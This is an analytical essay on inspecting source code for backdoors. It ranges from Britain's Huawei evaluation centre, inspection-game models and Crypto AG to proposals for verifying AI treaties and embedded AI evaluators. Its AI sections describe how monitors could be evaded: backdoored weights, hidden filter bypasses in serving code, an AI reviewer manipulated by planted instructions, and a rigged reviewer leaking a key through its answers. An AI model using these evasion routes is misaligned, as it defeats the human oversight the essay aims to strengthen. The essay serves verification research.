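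In April 2020, DCMS (then the department responsible for telecommunications) and the Ministry of Defence explained to a parliamentary committee why Britain both inspected Huawei's equipment and capped its use. Their written evidence, *The Security of 5G*, lists four main risks: backdoors, accidental flaws, vendors' remote access to equipment, and national dependence on a single supplier. They wrote that technical measures could reduce the first three but not the fourth. If Huawei stopped supplying updates, for example, a country that depended on it would be in trouble however well it had inspected the code. The cap limited that dependence, as well as how much of the network anyone could disrupt through a backdoor in Huawei's equipment.

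### What supporters, critics and Huawei made of it

The NCSC regarded the discovery of so many problems as a sign of "the model working properly". This is partly convincing, because HCSEC gave operators hundreds of specific warnings and ministers could claim that Britain knew more about Huawei and its risks than any other country did. But inspectors who had found nothing could also have said the model was working, so the number of findings doesn't show whether they would have caught a backdoor. The strongest evidence for the NCSC's view is that the inspectors investigated the build process and then publicly lowered the level of assurance they gave.

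Critics drew the opposite conclusion from the same findings. The law firm Skadden, in *UK Government Issues Report on Huawei* (2019), called that year's report the most detailed public expression of concern about Huawei's products by any national government, and thought it strengthened the American case against the company. The United States and Australia barred Huawei from their networks. Neither country needed to show that Huawei had planted a backdoor, because equipment with so many ordinary flaws gives any capable attacker a way in.

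*The 2019 Huawei cyber security evaluation report* (2019), a post on the software engineering blog The Shape of Code, speculates that many of the inspectors were recent graduates repeating what they had learned in class. A reader who had been through several such evaluations in North America found this unwarranted. The post also suggests that Huawei pay for an open centre outside government, whose staff would need no security clearance and could speak freely about any "spying code". Such a centre might convince customers who distrust GCHQ, but without vetting it would be easier for an intelligence service to infiltrate, and it would still depend on Huawei for money and code.

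Huawei presented the centre as proof of its openness and compared it to a glasshouse when it opened. Huawei's main argument was commercial, and one of its executives told the US Congress in 2012 that it would be "immensely foolish" for the company to risk involvement in espionage, because discovery would destroy its business. This argument has some force if the suspicion is that Huawei would spy on its own initiative, but less if the state orders it to cooperate. Huawei has also complained of paranoia and discrimination against its country of origin. It accepted the board's criticism of its engineering, although GCHQ reported that some senior staff had earlier tried to reduce the cost of meeting Britain's requirements.

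### American sanctions and the removal from 5G

In May 2019 the US government put Huawei on its Entity List, which restricts exports of American technology. It later added Huawei's British subsidiary, which then included HCSEC, so the sanctions also delayed some of the tools and equipment that the inspectors needed. Huawei began to replace American components, and HCSEC found that it would have to analyze hardware more to be equally confident in the redesigned products.

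A second set of sanctions, in May 2020, went further by restricting Huawei's use of American technology to design and make chips, including in factories outside the United States. The NCSC expected Huawei to switch to different chips and to new design tools that were "totally unknown to us". Like a compiler, such a tool can introduce a flaw that isn't in the design its users wrote, so the inspectors would have had to examine the tools as well as the products. The NCSC thought this would make oversight much harder and perhaps impossible.

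It therefore limited its plan for managing Huawei's risks to existing equipment, equipment that the new sanctions had not led Huawei to alter, and, for a transition period, fibre broadband. It advised operators not to buy the altered 5G equipment. On 14 July 2020 the government announced that operators would be banned from buying new Huawei 5G equipment after the end of that year and would have to remove their existing Huawei equipment from their 5G networks by the end of 2027.

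The government's stated reason was that the inspectors could no longer give enough assurance about future products. It did not claim that they had found a backdoor. The United States had been pressing its allies to exclude Huawei, which may also have influenced the decision. But the technical argument was serious, because most of what HCSEC had learned in ten years concerned particular products, and redesigning them would have made much of that knowledge obsolete.

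Parliament passed a law on telecommunications security in 2021, and in October 2022 the government used it to turn the advice on Huawei into legal directions to 35 operators. The directions kept the 2027 deadline.

### The centre since 2021

In November 2020, Huawei moved the centre into a separate company, Cyber Security Evaluations Limited, to free it from the sanctions. The new company was not on the Entity List, though Huawei remained its indirect owner. The company kept the old rules on independence. However, the board wrote in its 2021 report that a contractual matter, connected with uncertainty about the new law, had in practice limited the NCSC's freedom to choose which products the centre examined. The board insisted that no contract should limit this freedom.

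The board expected operators to submit far fewer new products. It still considered the centre essential because Huawei equipment would remain in British networks for years and keep needing updates. The 2027 deadline applies only to 5G, so some of that equipment may stay in use longer.

The government does not appear to have published another annual report since June 2021. CorpSignals' *Cyber Security Evaluations Limited*, which draws on the official company register, lists the company as still active in Banbury, with accounts filed up to the end of 2024. Endole's *Huawei Technologies (UK) Co Ltd* shows that the company shares several directors with Huawei's main British subsidiary. These records do not show how many inspectors the company employs or whether they can still match Huawei's source code to the binaries in use.

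## What a clean report is worth and when inspection deters

The inspectors in Banbury reported hundreds of flaws in Huawei's equipment, but the published reports don't identify any of them as a deliberate backdoor. How much a result like this should reassure a customer depends on how likely the inspection was to detect a backdoor and how likely there was to be one in the first place.

### Updating on a clean report

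Bayes' rule is the standard formula for revising a probability when new evidence arrives. Let *p* be the chance, before the inspection, that the product contains a backdoor, and let *d* be the detection probability. Assume that a product without a backdoor always gets a clean report. The chance that a product with a clean report contains a backdoor anyway is then

*p*(1 − *d*) / (*p*(1 − *d*) + 1 − *p*).

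If 50 of 1,000 products (5%) contain a backdoor, inspectors who detect 30% of backdoored products will find 15 and pass the other 35, along with the 950 clean products. A customer whose product passed therefore has a 35 in 985 chance, or about 3.6%, of owning a backdoored one. If the inspectors detect 90%, they pass only five backdoored products, and the chance falls to about 0.5%.

| Chance of a backdoor before inspection | After a clean report, if *d* is 30% | After a clean report, if *d* is 90% |
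|---|---|---|
| 5% | 3.6% | 0.5% |
| 20% | 15% | 2.4% |
| 50% | 41% | 9% |

The figures in the left-hand column are judgements about a particular vendor's motives, government and past conduct, and nobody can measure them. A government that starts at 50% and one that starts at 5% will still disagree after reading the same clean report, unless the inspection was very thorough.

The detection probability, *d*, is also uncertain. Experiments with planted backdoors have produced detection rates from under 20% to 90%, depending on the tool and the amount of code. *d* also has to cover the whole inspection, not just the reading of the code. If inspectors would recognise a backdoor 60% of the time, but there is a 50% chance that the vendor gave them the code containing it, *d* is 30%.

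A clean report soon loses much of its value if later updates aren't inspected. Suppose an excellent inspection reduces the chance that the software contains a backdoor to 0.5%, and the vendor then ships twelve monthly updates that nobody inspects, each with a 1% chance of introducing one. By the end of the year, the chance that the software contains at least one backdoor is about 12%.

### Inspectors who miss the same things

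A customer who doubts one inspector may hire a second. If each has a 30% chance of finding the backdoor and their results are independent, both miss it 49% of the time (0.7 × 0.7), so at least one finds it 51% of the time. If they miss exactly the same things, the chance of finding it stays at 30%, and the second clean report adds no information.

Most pairs of inspectors fall between full independence and complete overlap. Suppose half of all backdoors are crude, and each inspector independently finds 60% of those, while the other half are too subtle for any inspector to find. Each inspector then finds 30% of all backdoors, but two together find only 42%. Ten such inspectors would find almost every crude backdoor, or about 50% of the total, whereas ten fully independent inspectors with the same 30% rate would find 97%.

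It makes sense to hire teams that work differently, because two firms that run the same AI model over the same files are likely to miss many of the same backdoors. One team might read the source code while another fuzzes the binary and a third rebuilds the product.

### When hiding a backdoor stops paying

Avenhaus (2004), in *Applications of Inspection Games*, ranks deterrence first among an inspector's aims. If deterrence fails, the inspector aims to detect the violation as surely and as early as possible. An inspection that provides only weak evidence can still deter, because the developer must consider the consequences of being caught.

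Let *G* be what the developer gains from a backdoor that stays hidden, and *L* what the developer loses if inspectors catch it. With no backdoor, the developer gains and loses nothing. The expected value of hiding one is

(1 − *d*)*G* − *dL*,

which is negative when *d* is greater than *G*/(*G* + *L*). If the loss is four times the gain, the threshold is 1/5, or 20%. An inspection with a 30% detection probability would be enough to deter this developer, even though its clean report only lowers a 5% suspicion to 3.6%.

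These numbers are illustrative, because nobody has measured *G* or *L* for a real backdoor. The formula also assumes that the developer knows roughly how good the inspectors are, cares only about the average outcome, and gets no use out of a backdoor that the inspectors find. The most doubtful assumption is that inspectors who find a backdoor can show that it is one. Suppose they judge a planted flaw deliberate only one time in ten, and otherwise the developer apologises and repairs it at no cost. The expected loss on discovery is then *L*/10, and the threshold rises to

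*G*/(*G* + *L*/10) = 1/1.4,

or about 71%. Few inspections of a large product can hope to reach that. To bring the threshold back to 20%, the penalty would have to be 40 times the gain.

Late discovery weakens deterrence further. If the developer has already had half the benefit by the time the inspectors find the flaw, and they still blame the developer only one time in ten, then even certain discovery doesn't deter, because the developer keeps 0.5*G* and expects to lose only 0.4*G*. This is a strong reason to inspect a release before customers install it.

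False accusations also weaken deterrence, because they punish honest developers. *Inspection and crime prevention* (2013) describes models that include the chances of both false alarms and missed violations. In the example with a fourfold loss, a 10% chance of wrongly punishing an honest developer raises the threshold from 20% to 28%. So a customer can't solve the deniability problem just by treating every serious bug as sabotage.

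Whoever decides to plant a backdoor may not bear the loss if it is found. A state that orders a vendor to plant one collects the intelligence, while the vendor bears most of the commercial loss. For a rogue employee, *L* may be a prison sentence.

### Surprise inspections and stored copies

Inspectors who can't examine every release can still deter a developer from planting a backdoor if the developer doesn't know which releases they will choose. If they examine one release in three and would find a backdoor there 60% of the time, a backdoor in any given release has a 20% chance of being found. If the inspectors published their timetable, the developer would put the backdoor in a release they weren't going to examine.

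For this to work, the developer has to hand over the source of every release before learning which ones the inspectors will read. The British inspectors' arrangement with Huawei did not meet this condition, because Huawei had 30 days to supply source code after the inspectors requested it.

Game theorists have studied this kind of contest since the 1960s, beginning with arms control (Avenhaus, Von Stengel and Zamir, 2002, *Inspection games*). They now apply the same models to auditing and environmental surveillance. These models typically have a "mixed equilibrium", in which each side's best plan is to choose at random with particular probabilities, because the other side could exploit a predictable choice.

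In an early model by Dresher, an inspector has a fixed number of inspections to spread over a larger number of periods. The other side, called the inspectee, can count the visits and may commit one violation. Take two releases and a single inspection that never misses, and let *L* again be 4*G*. If the inspector examines the first release with probability *x*, planting a backdoor there is worth

(1 − *x*)*G* − 4*xG* = (1 − 5*x*)*G*.

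Waiting gives the developer an expected gain of *xG*, because the developer can safely use the second release if the inspection has already taken place, and stays honest if it hasn't. The two options are equal when *x* is 1/6, which limits the developer's expected gain to *G*/6. If the inspector always examined the same release, the developer would gain all of *G*.

Maschler later showed that the inspector does better by committing to such a plan in advance. As Von Stengel explains in *Recursive Inspection Games* (2014), the inspectee then acts legally as long as any inspections remain. In the example, the developer would cheat only in the one case in six where the inspector had used up the inspection early. Inspectors can therefore announce how often they sample, but they should avoid a known last visit, such as the one created when a contract ends on a fixed date while the vendor keeps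 shipping updates.

Von Stengel's own model allows several violations. The inspector's best plan doesn't depend on how many violations the inspectee intends or how much each is worth, so an inspector can follow it without knowing which violations have already gone undetected. That suits software, where nobody knows what backdoors earlier releases contained. A backdoor also tends to stay in the code from one release to the next, which gives inspectors more chances to find it than they have to catch a single illegal dumping of waste.

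If inspectors keep a copy of every release, the developer faces more risk, because better tools may later find a backdoor that the first inspection missed. Suppose the first inspection has a 10% chance of finding a backdoor, and the developer gains *G* if it is missed and loses 4*G* if it is found. Hiding one then brings an expected profit of 0.9*G* − 0.4*G* = 0.5*G*. If better tools later expose 30% of the backdoors that got through, the extra expected loss is 0.9 × 0.3 × 4*G* = 1.08*G*. The developer then expects to lose 0.58*G* overall, even with full use of the backdoor before it is exposed.

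Better tools are a realistic prospect, since AI models have already found flaws that reviewers and fuzzers missed for more than a decade. The copy can stay in a sealed store on the vendor's premises if the inspectors take its hash home. But a penalty that may come in fifteen years will not deter an official who expects to have retired by then, or a company that may no longer exist.

### Crypto AG and its suspicious customers

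Governments bought cipher machines from the Swiss company Crypto AG to protect diplomatic and military messages. In June 1970 the CIA and West Germany's foreign intelligence service, the BND, secretly became joint owners of the company. Crypto Museum's *Operation RUBICON*, a history based on internal papers from both agencies, describes Crypto AG as the preferred supplier to 80–90% of the world market afterward.

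Most of the rigged machines used an encryption procedure that was somewhat too weak, rather than a secret password. Someone who knew about the weakness and had enough computing power could break the encryption. By 1977 the NSA was reading about 57% of the enciphered messages it intercepted. Without Crypto AG, the estimated figure was 29% or less.

Several Crypto AG customers found weaknesses in its machines. Italy and Egypt had discovered a flaw in the H-460 by 1976 and demanded an explanation. The company took the machines back and fitted an improved procedure, different for each customer, which the NSA could still break with more computing. In June 1979 the Argentine navy found a weakness in the newer HC-500 series and summoned Crypto AG's chief executive to Buenos Aires, where he offered a repair that the NSA had designed. A further version in 1981 withstood an advanced attack by someone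 who already knew part of a message, but the agencies could exploit it as easily as before.

After the Falklands War of 1982, the Argentines learned that American and British intelligence had broken their systems. They summoned Crypto AG's mathematician, Kjell Ove Widman, who was secretly working with the agencies. Widman blamed an old analogue voice scrambler and insisted that the HC-500 machines were secure, and Argentina kept buying them.

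These customers found flaws but did not establish that they were deliberate, and each repair could pass as the correction of an honest mistake. Someone who collected the successive versions from several countries might have noticed that they all remained breakable, but each customer saw mainly its own machines. The commercial penalty was also small, because most rival makers were under Western control too. When Chile threatened to buy from a competitor, Datotek, Widman replied that Datotek would not get an export licence, knowing that the NSA would make sure of it.

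The comparison with source code inspection is loose, since these customers were testing machines and ciphers. But a state laboratory with a tip from an insider did little better. In 1977 Crypto AG's former head of research told the Swiss federal police that the company belonged to German and American intelligence and deliberately weakened machines meant for export. *Fall Crypto AG* (2020), a report by GPDel, the Swiss parliamentary committee that oversees the intelligence services, describes what followed. The army's signals office recommended examining a suspect machine from abroad but did not get one until 1982. A year later the office concluded that the accusation was neither proved nor conclusively refuted. The machine's circuits did not match the description in its manual, so the office couldn't rule out tampering.

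The police tried again in 1994, after Iran imprisoned a Crypto AG salesman, Hans Bühler, for nine months. They questioned Bühler and 20 other current and former employees and board members. Only two could describe any alleged tampering, and the rest had heard rumours. Switzerland's own foreign intelligence service had known since the autumn of 1993 that foreign agencies owned the company and that it exported weak machines, but it kept this from the country's political leaders.

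Inspection may have deterred Crypto AG from selling weak machines to the Swiss authorities. The committee believes the company never did so, and considers the authorities' ability to check their machines and even influence the design important. But the owners had originally agreed that Switzerland, Sweden and the NATO countries could buy secure equipment, so the Swiss might have received secure machines even without inspecting them.

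The ability to inspect did not protect them from another Swiss maker. *The report of a Swiss investigation into the case of Crypto AG* (2020), which translates and supplements the committee's summary, recounts that a second company sold insecure devices to the federal government and two large corporations. The defence ministry learned of this sometime between 2002 and 2008 and closed the security hole. The Swiss broadcaster SRF later identified the company as Omnisec and reported that its customers had included the Swiss intelligence services.

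### Routers intercepted on the way to the customer

An attacker can also tamper with the finished equipment without touching the vendor's source code. In May 2014 the journalist Glenn Greenwald published an internal NSA newsletter from June 2010, leaked by Edward Snowden. Network Computing's *NSA Allegedly Installs Backdoors On US Network Devices* (2014) recounts how the agency intercepted routers and servers that American companies were exporting, added surveillance tools, resealed the boxes and sent them on. Engadget's *Latest Snowden leak reveals the NSA intercepted and bugged Cisco routers* (2014) describes a photograph of an NSA team at work on a Cisco router.

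One implant contacted the NSA's hidden servers several months after the interception, and the agency used the connection to explore the customer's network, according to a fuller version of the document quoted in Schneier on Security's *Cisco Shipping Equipment to Fake Addresses to Foil NSA Interception* (2015). Dark Reading's *NSA Reportedly Adds Backdoors To US-Made Routers* reports that it is unclear how often the NSA used the method.

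A customer could have inspected every line of Cisco's source code, rebuilt the binary and matched it to the official release without learning anything about this router. The useful check is to read the software out of the device after delivery and compare it with the approved binary. That would miss an implant on an added chip that leaves the software unchanged, so somebody may also have to open the case and compare the circuit board with a trusted one.

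Cisco's chief executive, John Chambers, complained to President Obama. Cisco said in its *Customer Recommendations* that it took the allegations "very seriously". It also shipped equipment to fake addresses, which makes interception harder because the agency has to work out which parcel is going to its target.

### Deterrence or diversion

Supporters of inspection argue that a developer who expects scrutiny will leave the backdoor out. Sceptics reply that the developer, or the state behind it, will choose a subtler flaw or a later point of entry. There is little direct evidence for either claim, because an attacker who gives up leaves nothing for inspectors to find and intelligence agencies rarely publish their reasons for rejecting a plan. The absence of a proven backdoor in Huawei's equipment is equally consistent with successful deterrence, an honest vendor, or a backdoor that the inspectors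 missed.

Crypto AG provides the best evidence about subtler methods. When customers complained, the agencies continued the operation with weaknesses that were harder to find, though some of the repairs meant that messages took more resources to read. By the late 1980s, as academic research on encryption spread, the NSA knew it would find it increasingly hard to design procedures that outsiders would accept and it could still break. Scrutiny had made the work harder, but the CIA thought it worth continuing and bought out its German partner in 1994.

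The evidence that inspection pushes attackers to later points of entry is weaker. The XZ Utils attacker put the crucial script in the release package, outside the repository that people were more likely to read. The NSA tampered with routers after they had left the factory. These cases show that attackers use places a source code reviewer doesn't check, but not that they would have put their backdoors in the source code if nobody had been inspecting it. A spy agency may prefer interception anyway, because it affects only the chosen customer and doesn't require the vendor's help.

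A better test would compare products or countries before and after inspection began, using records of what attackers tried. Leaked archives might one day make this possible. Until then, nobody can say what share of attackers an inspection deters and what share it only redirects.

Inspection can still be worthwhile if it only diverts an attacker to another method. A backdoor in a router's source code reaches every customer who installs the release, while an agency that intercepts parcels has to find, open and reseal them one at a time. If inspection forces an attacker to switch from backdoors to interception, most customers are safer, although the few whom the agency most wants to watch may be no better off.

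If the attacker could gain *V* by another route, planting the backdoor in the source code stops being the better choice once *d* exceeds (*G* − *V*)/(*G* + *L*). When *L* is four times *G* and *V* is half of *G*, the threshold drops from 20% to 10%. An attacker with a good alternative is therefore easier to deter from using the source code, but in this example still expects to gain half of *G* unless someone also checks the builds, updates and deliveries.

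## Inspecting the code that trains and runs AI models

Inspectors can read the source code that trains an AI model, runs it for users and controls the chips, just as they can read any other code. But the model itself consists mainly of weights, billions of numbers that training adjusts until the model behaves as its developer wants, and nobody can read those the way a programmer reads source code.

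Most proposals for inspecting the code that trains and runs AI models concern treaties. *An International Agreement to Prevent the Premature Creation of Artificial Superintelligence* (Scher, Abecassis and colleagues, 2025) proposes an agreement, led by the United States and China, that would ban training runs of more than 10^24 arithmetic operations and require monitoring of those above 10^22. To enforce such limits, inspectors would have to know what thousands of chips are doing in another country's data centres. A backdoor could make those chips report less computation than they performed. A backdoor in the inspectors' own equipment could also copy the inspected country's models.

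Inspectors would have four kinds of code to read:

- The training code determines which data the model learns from, by what method and for how long. A developer could use it to plant a backdoor in the weights.
- The serving code passes users' requests to the finished model and applies safety filters. A hidden condition could switch the filters off for chosen users or send them to a different model.
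- The chips' system software and firmware (the low-level code stored in the hardware) load the other programs and report what is running.
- Verification devices, such as taps on the cables between chips, run code of their own. Both sides have to trust it.

### Reading the project's code

The simplest proposal is to let inspectors into the AI project with enough access to review the code and confirm that no large training run is taking place (Scher and Thiergart, 2024, *Mechanisms to Verify International Agreements About AI Development*). Scher and Thiergart rate the feasibility as medium and estimate that it would take one to two years to prepare. The technical work isn't particularly difficult, but the inspectors would see much that the developer wants to keep secret. A valuable training method may be only a few lines long, so clean-room rules against copying would do little to protect it.

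Scher and Thiergart also warn that inspectors might not be able to tell whether the code they are shown is the code that runs. Britain's inspectors had the same difficulty with Huawei. AI training can be checked in a way that resembles rebuilding a binary. The developer keeps a full record of the run, including the code, data, settings and periodic snapshots of the weights. Inspectors pick a short segment, run the recorded code from one snapshot and check whether it produces the next. Repeating 1% of the run takes roughly 1% of the computing power, and if the inspectors choose the segments at random, the developer can't prepare only those segments.

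Someone has to do this in a data centre that both sides trust not to leak the weights, and none exists yet. The comparison may also need some tolerance, because AI chips don't always give exactly the same result when they repeat a calculation. A developer could try to hide small changes within that tolerance. It could also declare one enormous run as several small ones, each starting from the weights the previous one produced. To prevent this, Scher and Thiergart suggest that every run start from random weights generated in an agreed way, so that inspectors can generate the same weights and compare them.

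In a less intrusive version, inspectors read the code less often. They first record power use and network traffic while the developer runs its usual, permitted programs. Afterwards they only take measurements, and ask to see the code again if the pattern changes. A state could try to make a forbidden run look like a permitted one. Scher and Thiergart think it could disguise one such measurement, how busy the chips are, if it accepted perhaps 20% higher costs, which a government could afford. Faking several measurements at once should be harder, but nobody has shown how much harder.

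### An AI reviewer that reports only violations

If the main objection is that inspectors would learn too much, an AI model could read the code for them. *Verifying Restrictions on Frontier AI Research* (Scher, 2026) proposes that an AI screen all the production and research code at organisations likely to break an agreement, and perhaps their experiment logs and documents too. The AI would report only findings that bear on compliance, for example that a program contains a new and forbidden training algorithm, and the human inspectors would never see the program itself. *Verifying International Agreements on AI* (Baker, Kulp et al., 2025) adds that the inspected side can wipe an AI's memory afterwards, which it can't do with a human auditor.

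Scher identifies two difficulties with using AI to review this code. First, outside inspectors must be able to confirm that the right review happens every time, or the developer could submit a cleaned-up copy. One way to check is to hash the files the AI reads and compare the result with a hash of the files the chips load. Second, the AI must be skilled enough to review the code well, must not sabotage the process, and must resist manipulation, such as instructions hidden in the code. Existing AI reviewers miss many planted attacks, especially in large batches of code, and a developer with access to the same reviewer can rewrite a forbidden program until it passes.

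The inspecting state will therefore want to keep its reviewer secret, while the developer will want to know that the reviewer isn't stealing anything. Confidential computing may satisfy both, because it runs a program in a part of the machine that even the machine's owner can't look into. *Verification for International AI Governance*, by Harack, Trager and colleagues, describes how both sides could examine the code that manages the review before it runs, while the developer's model and the inspectors' tests stay hidden. Recent AI chips already support confidential computing, but the version on Nvidia's Hopper chips isn't meant to withstand sophisticated physical attacks, and a state that owns the building can open the machine.

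Restricting the AI to yes-or-no answers doesn't prevent every leak either. A rigged reviewer could encode a secret in its sequence of answers. A typical encryption key is 256 bits long, so 256 answers could carry it. The developer can reduce this risk by limiting the number of reviews and having the AI explain each accusation to the developer's own staff first.

Inspectors can't review code on computers they don't know about. Scher considers secret data centres the hardest problem for an agreement that restricts AI research. A study he cites found that developers had worked out about half of the new methods behind two leading models, Llama 3 and DeepSeek-V3, with less computing power than eight Nvidia H100 chips provide. The 2025 draft agreement would allow anyone to keep up to 16 such chips, worth about $500,000, outside monitored facilities, so a small team could use them to develop a forbidden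 method without inspection.

The team would still need a large cluster to get the full benefit, and inspectors would probably be monitoring the largest ones. Scher wants them to review the code for all substantial training on those clusters and look for relevant methods that weren't already known. Focusing on large clusters is sensible because a state can hide a few dozen chips far more easily than a hundred thousand. For the secret sites, he trusts whistleblowers and intelligence agencies more than any kind of code review.

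### What Apple's servers can prove

Whoever reads the code, the inspectors need evidence that a distant machine is running the version they approved. Apple has built the best-known public system for this. In June 2024 it announced servers for AI requests that are too demanding for an iPhone, and Apple's *Private Cloud Compute* presents them as an extension of the phone's own security and privacy to the cloud. Customers can't enter Apple's data centres to check. Instead, their phones demand an attestation, a signed statement by the server's hardware of what software it is running. In outline, attestation works as follows:

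1. The manufacturer puts a secret key in the chip and vouches for the matching public key.
2. When the server starts, it hashes each piece of software before running it.
3. The chip signs these hashes with its secret key and sends them to the phone.
4. The phone checks the signature and compares the hashes with a public list of releases. If they don't match, it sends no data.

The list is a public log like the one Google keeps for its Pixel phones. Apple also promised to publish every binary it uses on these servers, according to a statement quoted by 9to5Mac, including the operating system, the applications and, for the first time on any Apple platform, two important pieces of firmware in unencrypted form. The programmer Willison (2024) thought these enforceable guarantees were the most impressive part of the design, because they address what happens if Apple changes the code later.

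That October, Apple gave outside researchers tools to examine the releases. MacRumors' *Apple Shares Private Cloud Compute Virtual Research Environment, Provides Bounties for Vulnerabilities* (2024) explains that researchers can run a copy of the server software on a Mac, modify it and check that the log is consistent. But Apple published source code only for selected components, so researchers have to analyse the rest as binaries, which is slower. As an incentive, Apple offers rewards of up to $1 million for the most serious kind of flaw, according to AppleInsider.

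These measures protect customers well against an intruder or a rogue employee who installs altered software on a server, because the phones would not communicate with that server. They are weaker against Apple itself. Apple designs the chips, and anyone who kept a copy of a chip's secret key could sign a false statement on a different machine. Apple also writes the iPhone software that checks the statement. And if the published binary contains a backdoor, a server running it will pass the check with a true statement. The public record still makes planting a backdoor riskier for Apple than for a company that publishes nothing.

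Attestation can also cover a model's weights. Scher and Thiergart suggest using it to confirm that the developer is using the same model that evaluators tested. This proves that the weights are the same, but they could still contain a backdoor.

### Checking every layer of an untrusted machine

Two rival states can't rely on one manufacturer as Apple's customers do. Baker and colleagues assume the worst case, in which the chip designer, the factory and the data centre operator may all be working for the government under inspection. Somebody then has to disclose the design of every layer of the machine, confirm that the disclosed design is the real one, test it for flaws and fix any they find. The layers include the hypervisor, which keeps operating systems on the same machine separate.

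| Layer | Confirming that it is the real one | Repairing flaws |
|---|---|---|
| Applications, operating system and hypervisor | Each program checks the next before starting it; a trusted compiler builds them | Software updates |
| Firmware | The same start-up checks, plus a scan of the memory that stores it | Updates, but some firmware is permanent |
| Hardware | Experts take apart and scan a random sample of chips, or watch the factory | Stop using the chip, or verify in another way |

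For disclosure, Baker and colleagues suggest open-source components, published designs, or a supplier the inspectors already trust. For testing, they suggest formal verification and teams paid to attack the system. They mark many of these steps as technically ambitious.

Thoroughly inspecting source code looks feasible only for small programs. Linux has millions of lines, and people have found more than 1,000 security vulnerabilities in it in recent years. Some open-source hypervisors have only tens of thousands of lines, and an operating system built solely for verification could leave out graphics and most device support. A team of five, each reading 100 lines an hour for four hours a day, could read 50,000 lines in 25 working days. A program that small could also be formally verified, at least with better proof tools. Baker and colleagues add that the developer's own applications don't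 have to be free of flaws, as long as the inspectors' software works correctly.

The strongest part of the proposal is using a small program to confine all the other code. The inspectors' task would then be closer to checking a few hundred lines of a voting program than to checking Huawei's vast and disorderly code, which defeated its inspectors. This works only if the small program confines everything else, which depends on the layers below it.

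Firmware is harder to check because it reports its own hash, so a malicious version can report the hash of the approved one, much as Thompson's compiler hid its own backdoor. Inspectors can avoid this by reading the memory chip directly, and they may need to do so only for the first program that runs at start-up. They also have to prevent anyone from swapping the firmware after the check. Baker and colleagues suggest demanding a new attestation at random moments, with too little time to reply for the operator to restore the approved version first.

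The chip sits below the firmware. A modern AI chip has tens of billions of transistors in dozens of layers, and Harack and colleagues know of no way to image them all without destroying the chip. There is also no known way to prove that two chips are identical, so inspectors who take one apart can't be certain that their findings apply to another.

Sampling can still work against some forms of cheating. Suppose a data centre has 10,000 chips and inspectors destroy 300 chosen at random, which would cost about $9 million at 2025 prices. If the state has altered 1% of the chips, the inspectors have a 95% chance of picking at least one altered chip. If the state needs to alter only one chip, their chance of picking it is 3%. Harack and colleagues make the same distinction, giving the example of one rigged chip that gets inside a protected group and reads the data the other chips exchange. Picking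 an altered chip helps only if the experts recognise the alteration.

Inspectors could instead watch the chips being made, but the leading manufacturers would be showing a rival state their most valuable trade secrets.

### Devices that both sides have to trust

Because advanced chips are hard to check, Harack and colleagues prefer to put much of the verification equipment outside them. The AI chips do the heavy computing inside an enclosure, and a simpler device at its boundary records or restricts what goes in and out. This device can use older chips with a single layer of circuits, which experts can image reliably, and it can work with AI chips that are already in use.

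The inspected state fears that the device will send its models abroad, while the inspecting state fears that the other will tamper with the device. Harack and colleagues want both states to examine the hardware and the code, as American and Soviet teams did when they developed equipment for nuclear verification. Rival teams could work together in private, or publish the design and pay anyone who finds a flaw. The inspectors would keep only some of their test material secret. Baker and colleagues note that openness also helps a cheater look for weaknesses, and suggest keeping some mechanisms confidential as well.

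Cameras, seals and sensors would then guard the device. If each has its own secret key, an attacker has to defeat all of them at once. The inspecting state can also install devices from several manufacturers and compare their results, since unrelated manufacturers are unlikely to have planted the same backdoor.

The device still has to analyse what it records. Baker and colleagues list as an open problem how to show, from the traffic between a group of chips, that the chips ran only the declared program. Until someone solves it, a state could hide forbidden work in traffic that looks legitimate. Baker and colleagues expect that it will be possible to circumvent the technical methods until much more research is done. Harack and colleagues are somewhat more optimistic, and think a few years of serious effort could make rules on computing in data centres verifiable.

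An earlier proposal would give inspectors much less access. *AI Verification* (Mittelsteadt, 2021), written for the Center for Security and Emerging Technology (CSET) at Georgetown University, considers how to check that AI can't fire a military drone's weapons. Inspectors would read only the code that controls the weapons, which the paper calls a verification zone. They would treat everything else, including the operating system and navigation software, as a closed box that might contain AI. A short program at the edge of the zone, called a checkpoint, would accept a command to fire only from a human operator, and inspectors could read the program in full.

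The closed operating system is a serious weakness. On most computers, the operating system loads every other program and can change those programs in memory, so a state could hide code in it that bypasses the checkpoint. Mittelsteadt's alternative of physically separating the zones is safer, because an operating system can't easily alter a computer it isn't connected to. Neither arrangement can show whether the human operator is making a decision or just approving whatever an AI recommends.

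A state could also change the weapons code as soon as the inspectors left. Mittelsteadt suggests the inspectors keep a hash of the code and check the code against it on their next visit, or fit a device that hashes the code from time to time and broadcasts the result. If the device gets the file through the drone's own software, that software can supply the approved copy while the drone runs different code. The device therefore has to read the drone's memory directly, so the drone's owner has to allow a foreign device inside a weapon. Harack and colleagues expect detailed regulation of AI weapons to remain politically difficult even with the best methods.

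### Evaluators inside AI companies

These schemes for states have not been put into practice, but two American companies have voluntarily given outsiders access, and that access has grown quickly. In 2025, METR, a nonprofit that assesses dangerous abilities in AI models, reviewed a pilot risk report by Anthropic. Anthropic supplied all the evidence, which consisted of internal documents, written answers and interviews with important employees. METR could therefore judge whether the evidence was consistent but had little chance to discover what was missing.

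For METR's *Frontier Risk Report (February to March 2026)*, the participating companies gave METR access to their most capable internal models, including the unedited reasoning the models write before they answer. The companies also described how they used and monitored AI internally. They then approved which non-public information METR could disclose.

In October 2026, Anthropic announced in *An update on independent evaluators* that six METR staff now had access similar to an employee's. It compared them to the examiners regulators station inside banks. According to the announcement, Anthropic can't veto their reports, though it can require narrow redactions, and its other evaluators have less access and more limited rights to publish.

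OpenAI followed in mid-November with *Our first phase of embedded assessments*, which names METR, Apollo Research, Transluce and Goodfire as the four participating organisations. Each works within an agreed scope. OpenAI says that they publish independently, but that it can redact confidential information and ask them to delay publication. Since the launch of GPT-4, OpenAI had already given outside teams early versions of its models to test for particular abilities, such as hacking or deception.

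An evaluator who works inside a company can pursue questions the company didn't expect, as British officials did when they asked Huawei about OpenSSL. METR's staff may be able to do this at Anthropic. OpenAI's assessors can pursue such questions only if they fall within the assessment's scope, and a developer with something to hide would try to exclude them.

Narrow redaction is less of a problem, since readers can see that something is missing and ask about it. Delay may matter more, because companies replace their models every few months and a late report may describe a model that customers no longer use. Such a report could still reveal a fault in the way the company works.

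These arrangements focus on how models behave and how companies manage them. An evaluator with an employee's access might also read some of the source code, but that alone wouldn't show which code runs on the company's servers. The SolarWinds intruders inserted their backdoor during the build process, where most employees would never have seen it. Evaluators are also a poor defence against a secret government order, because the company would have to exclude them from anything connected with it.

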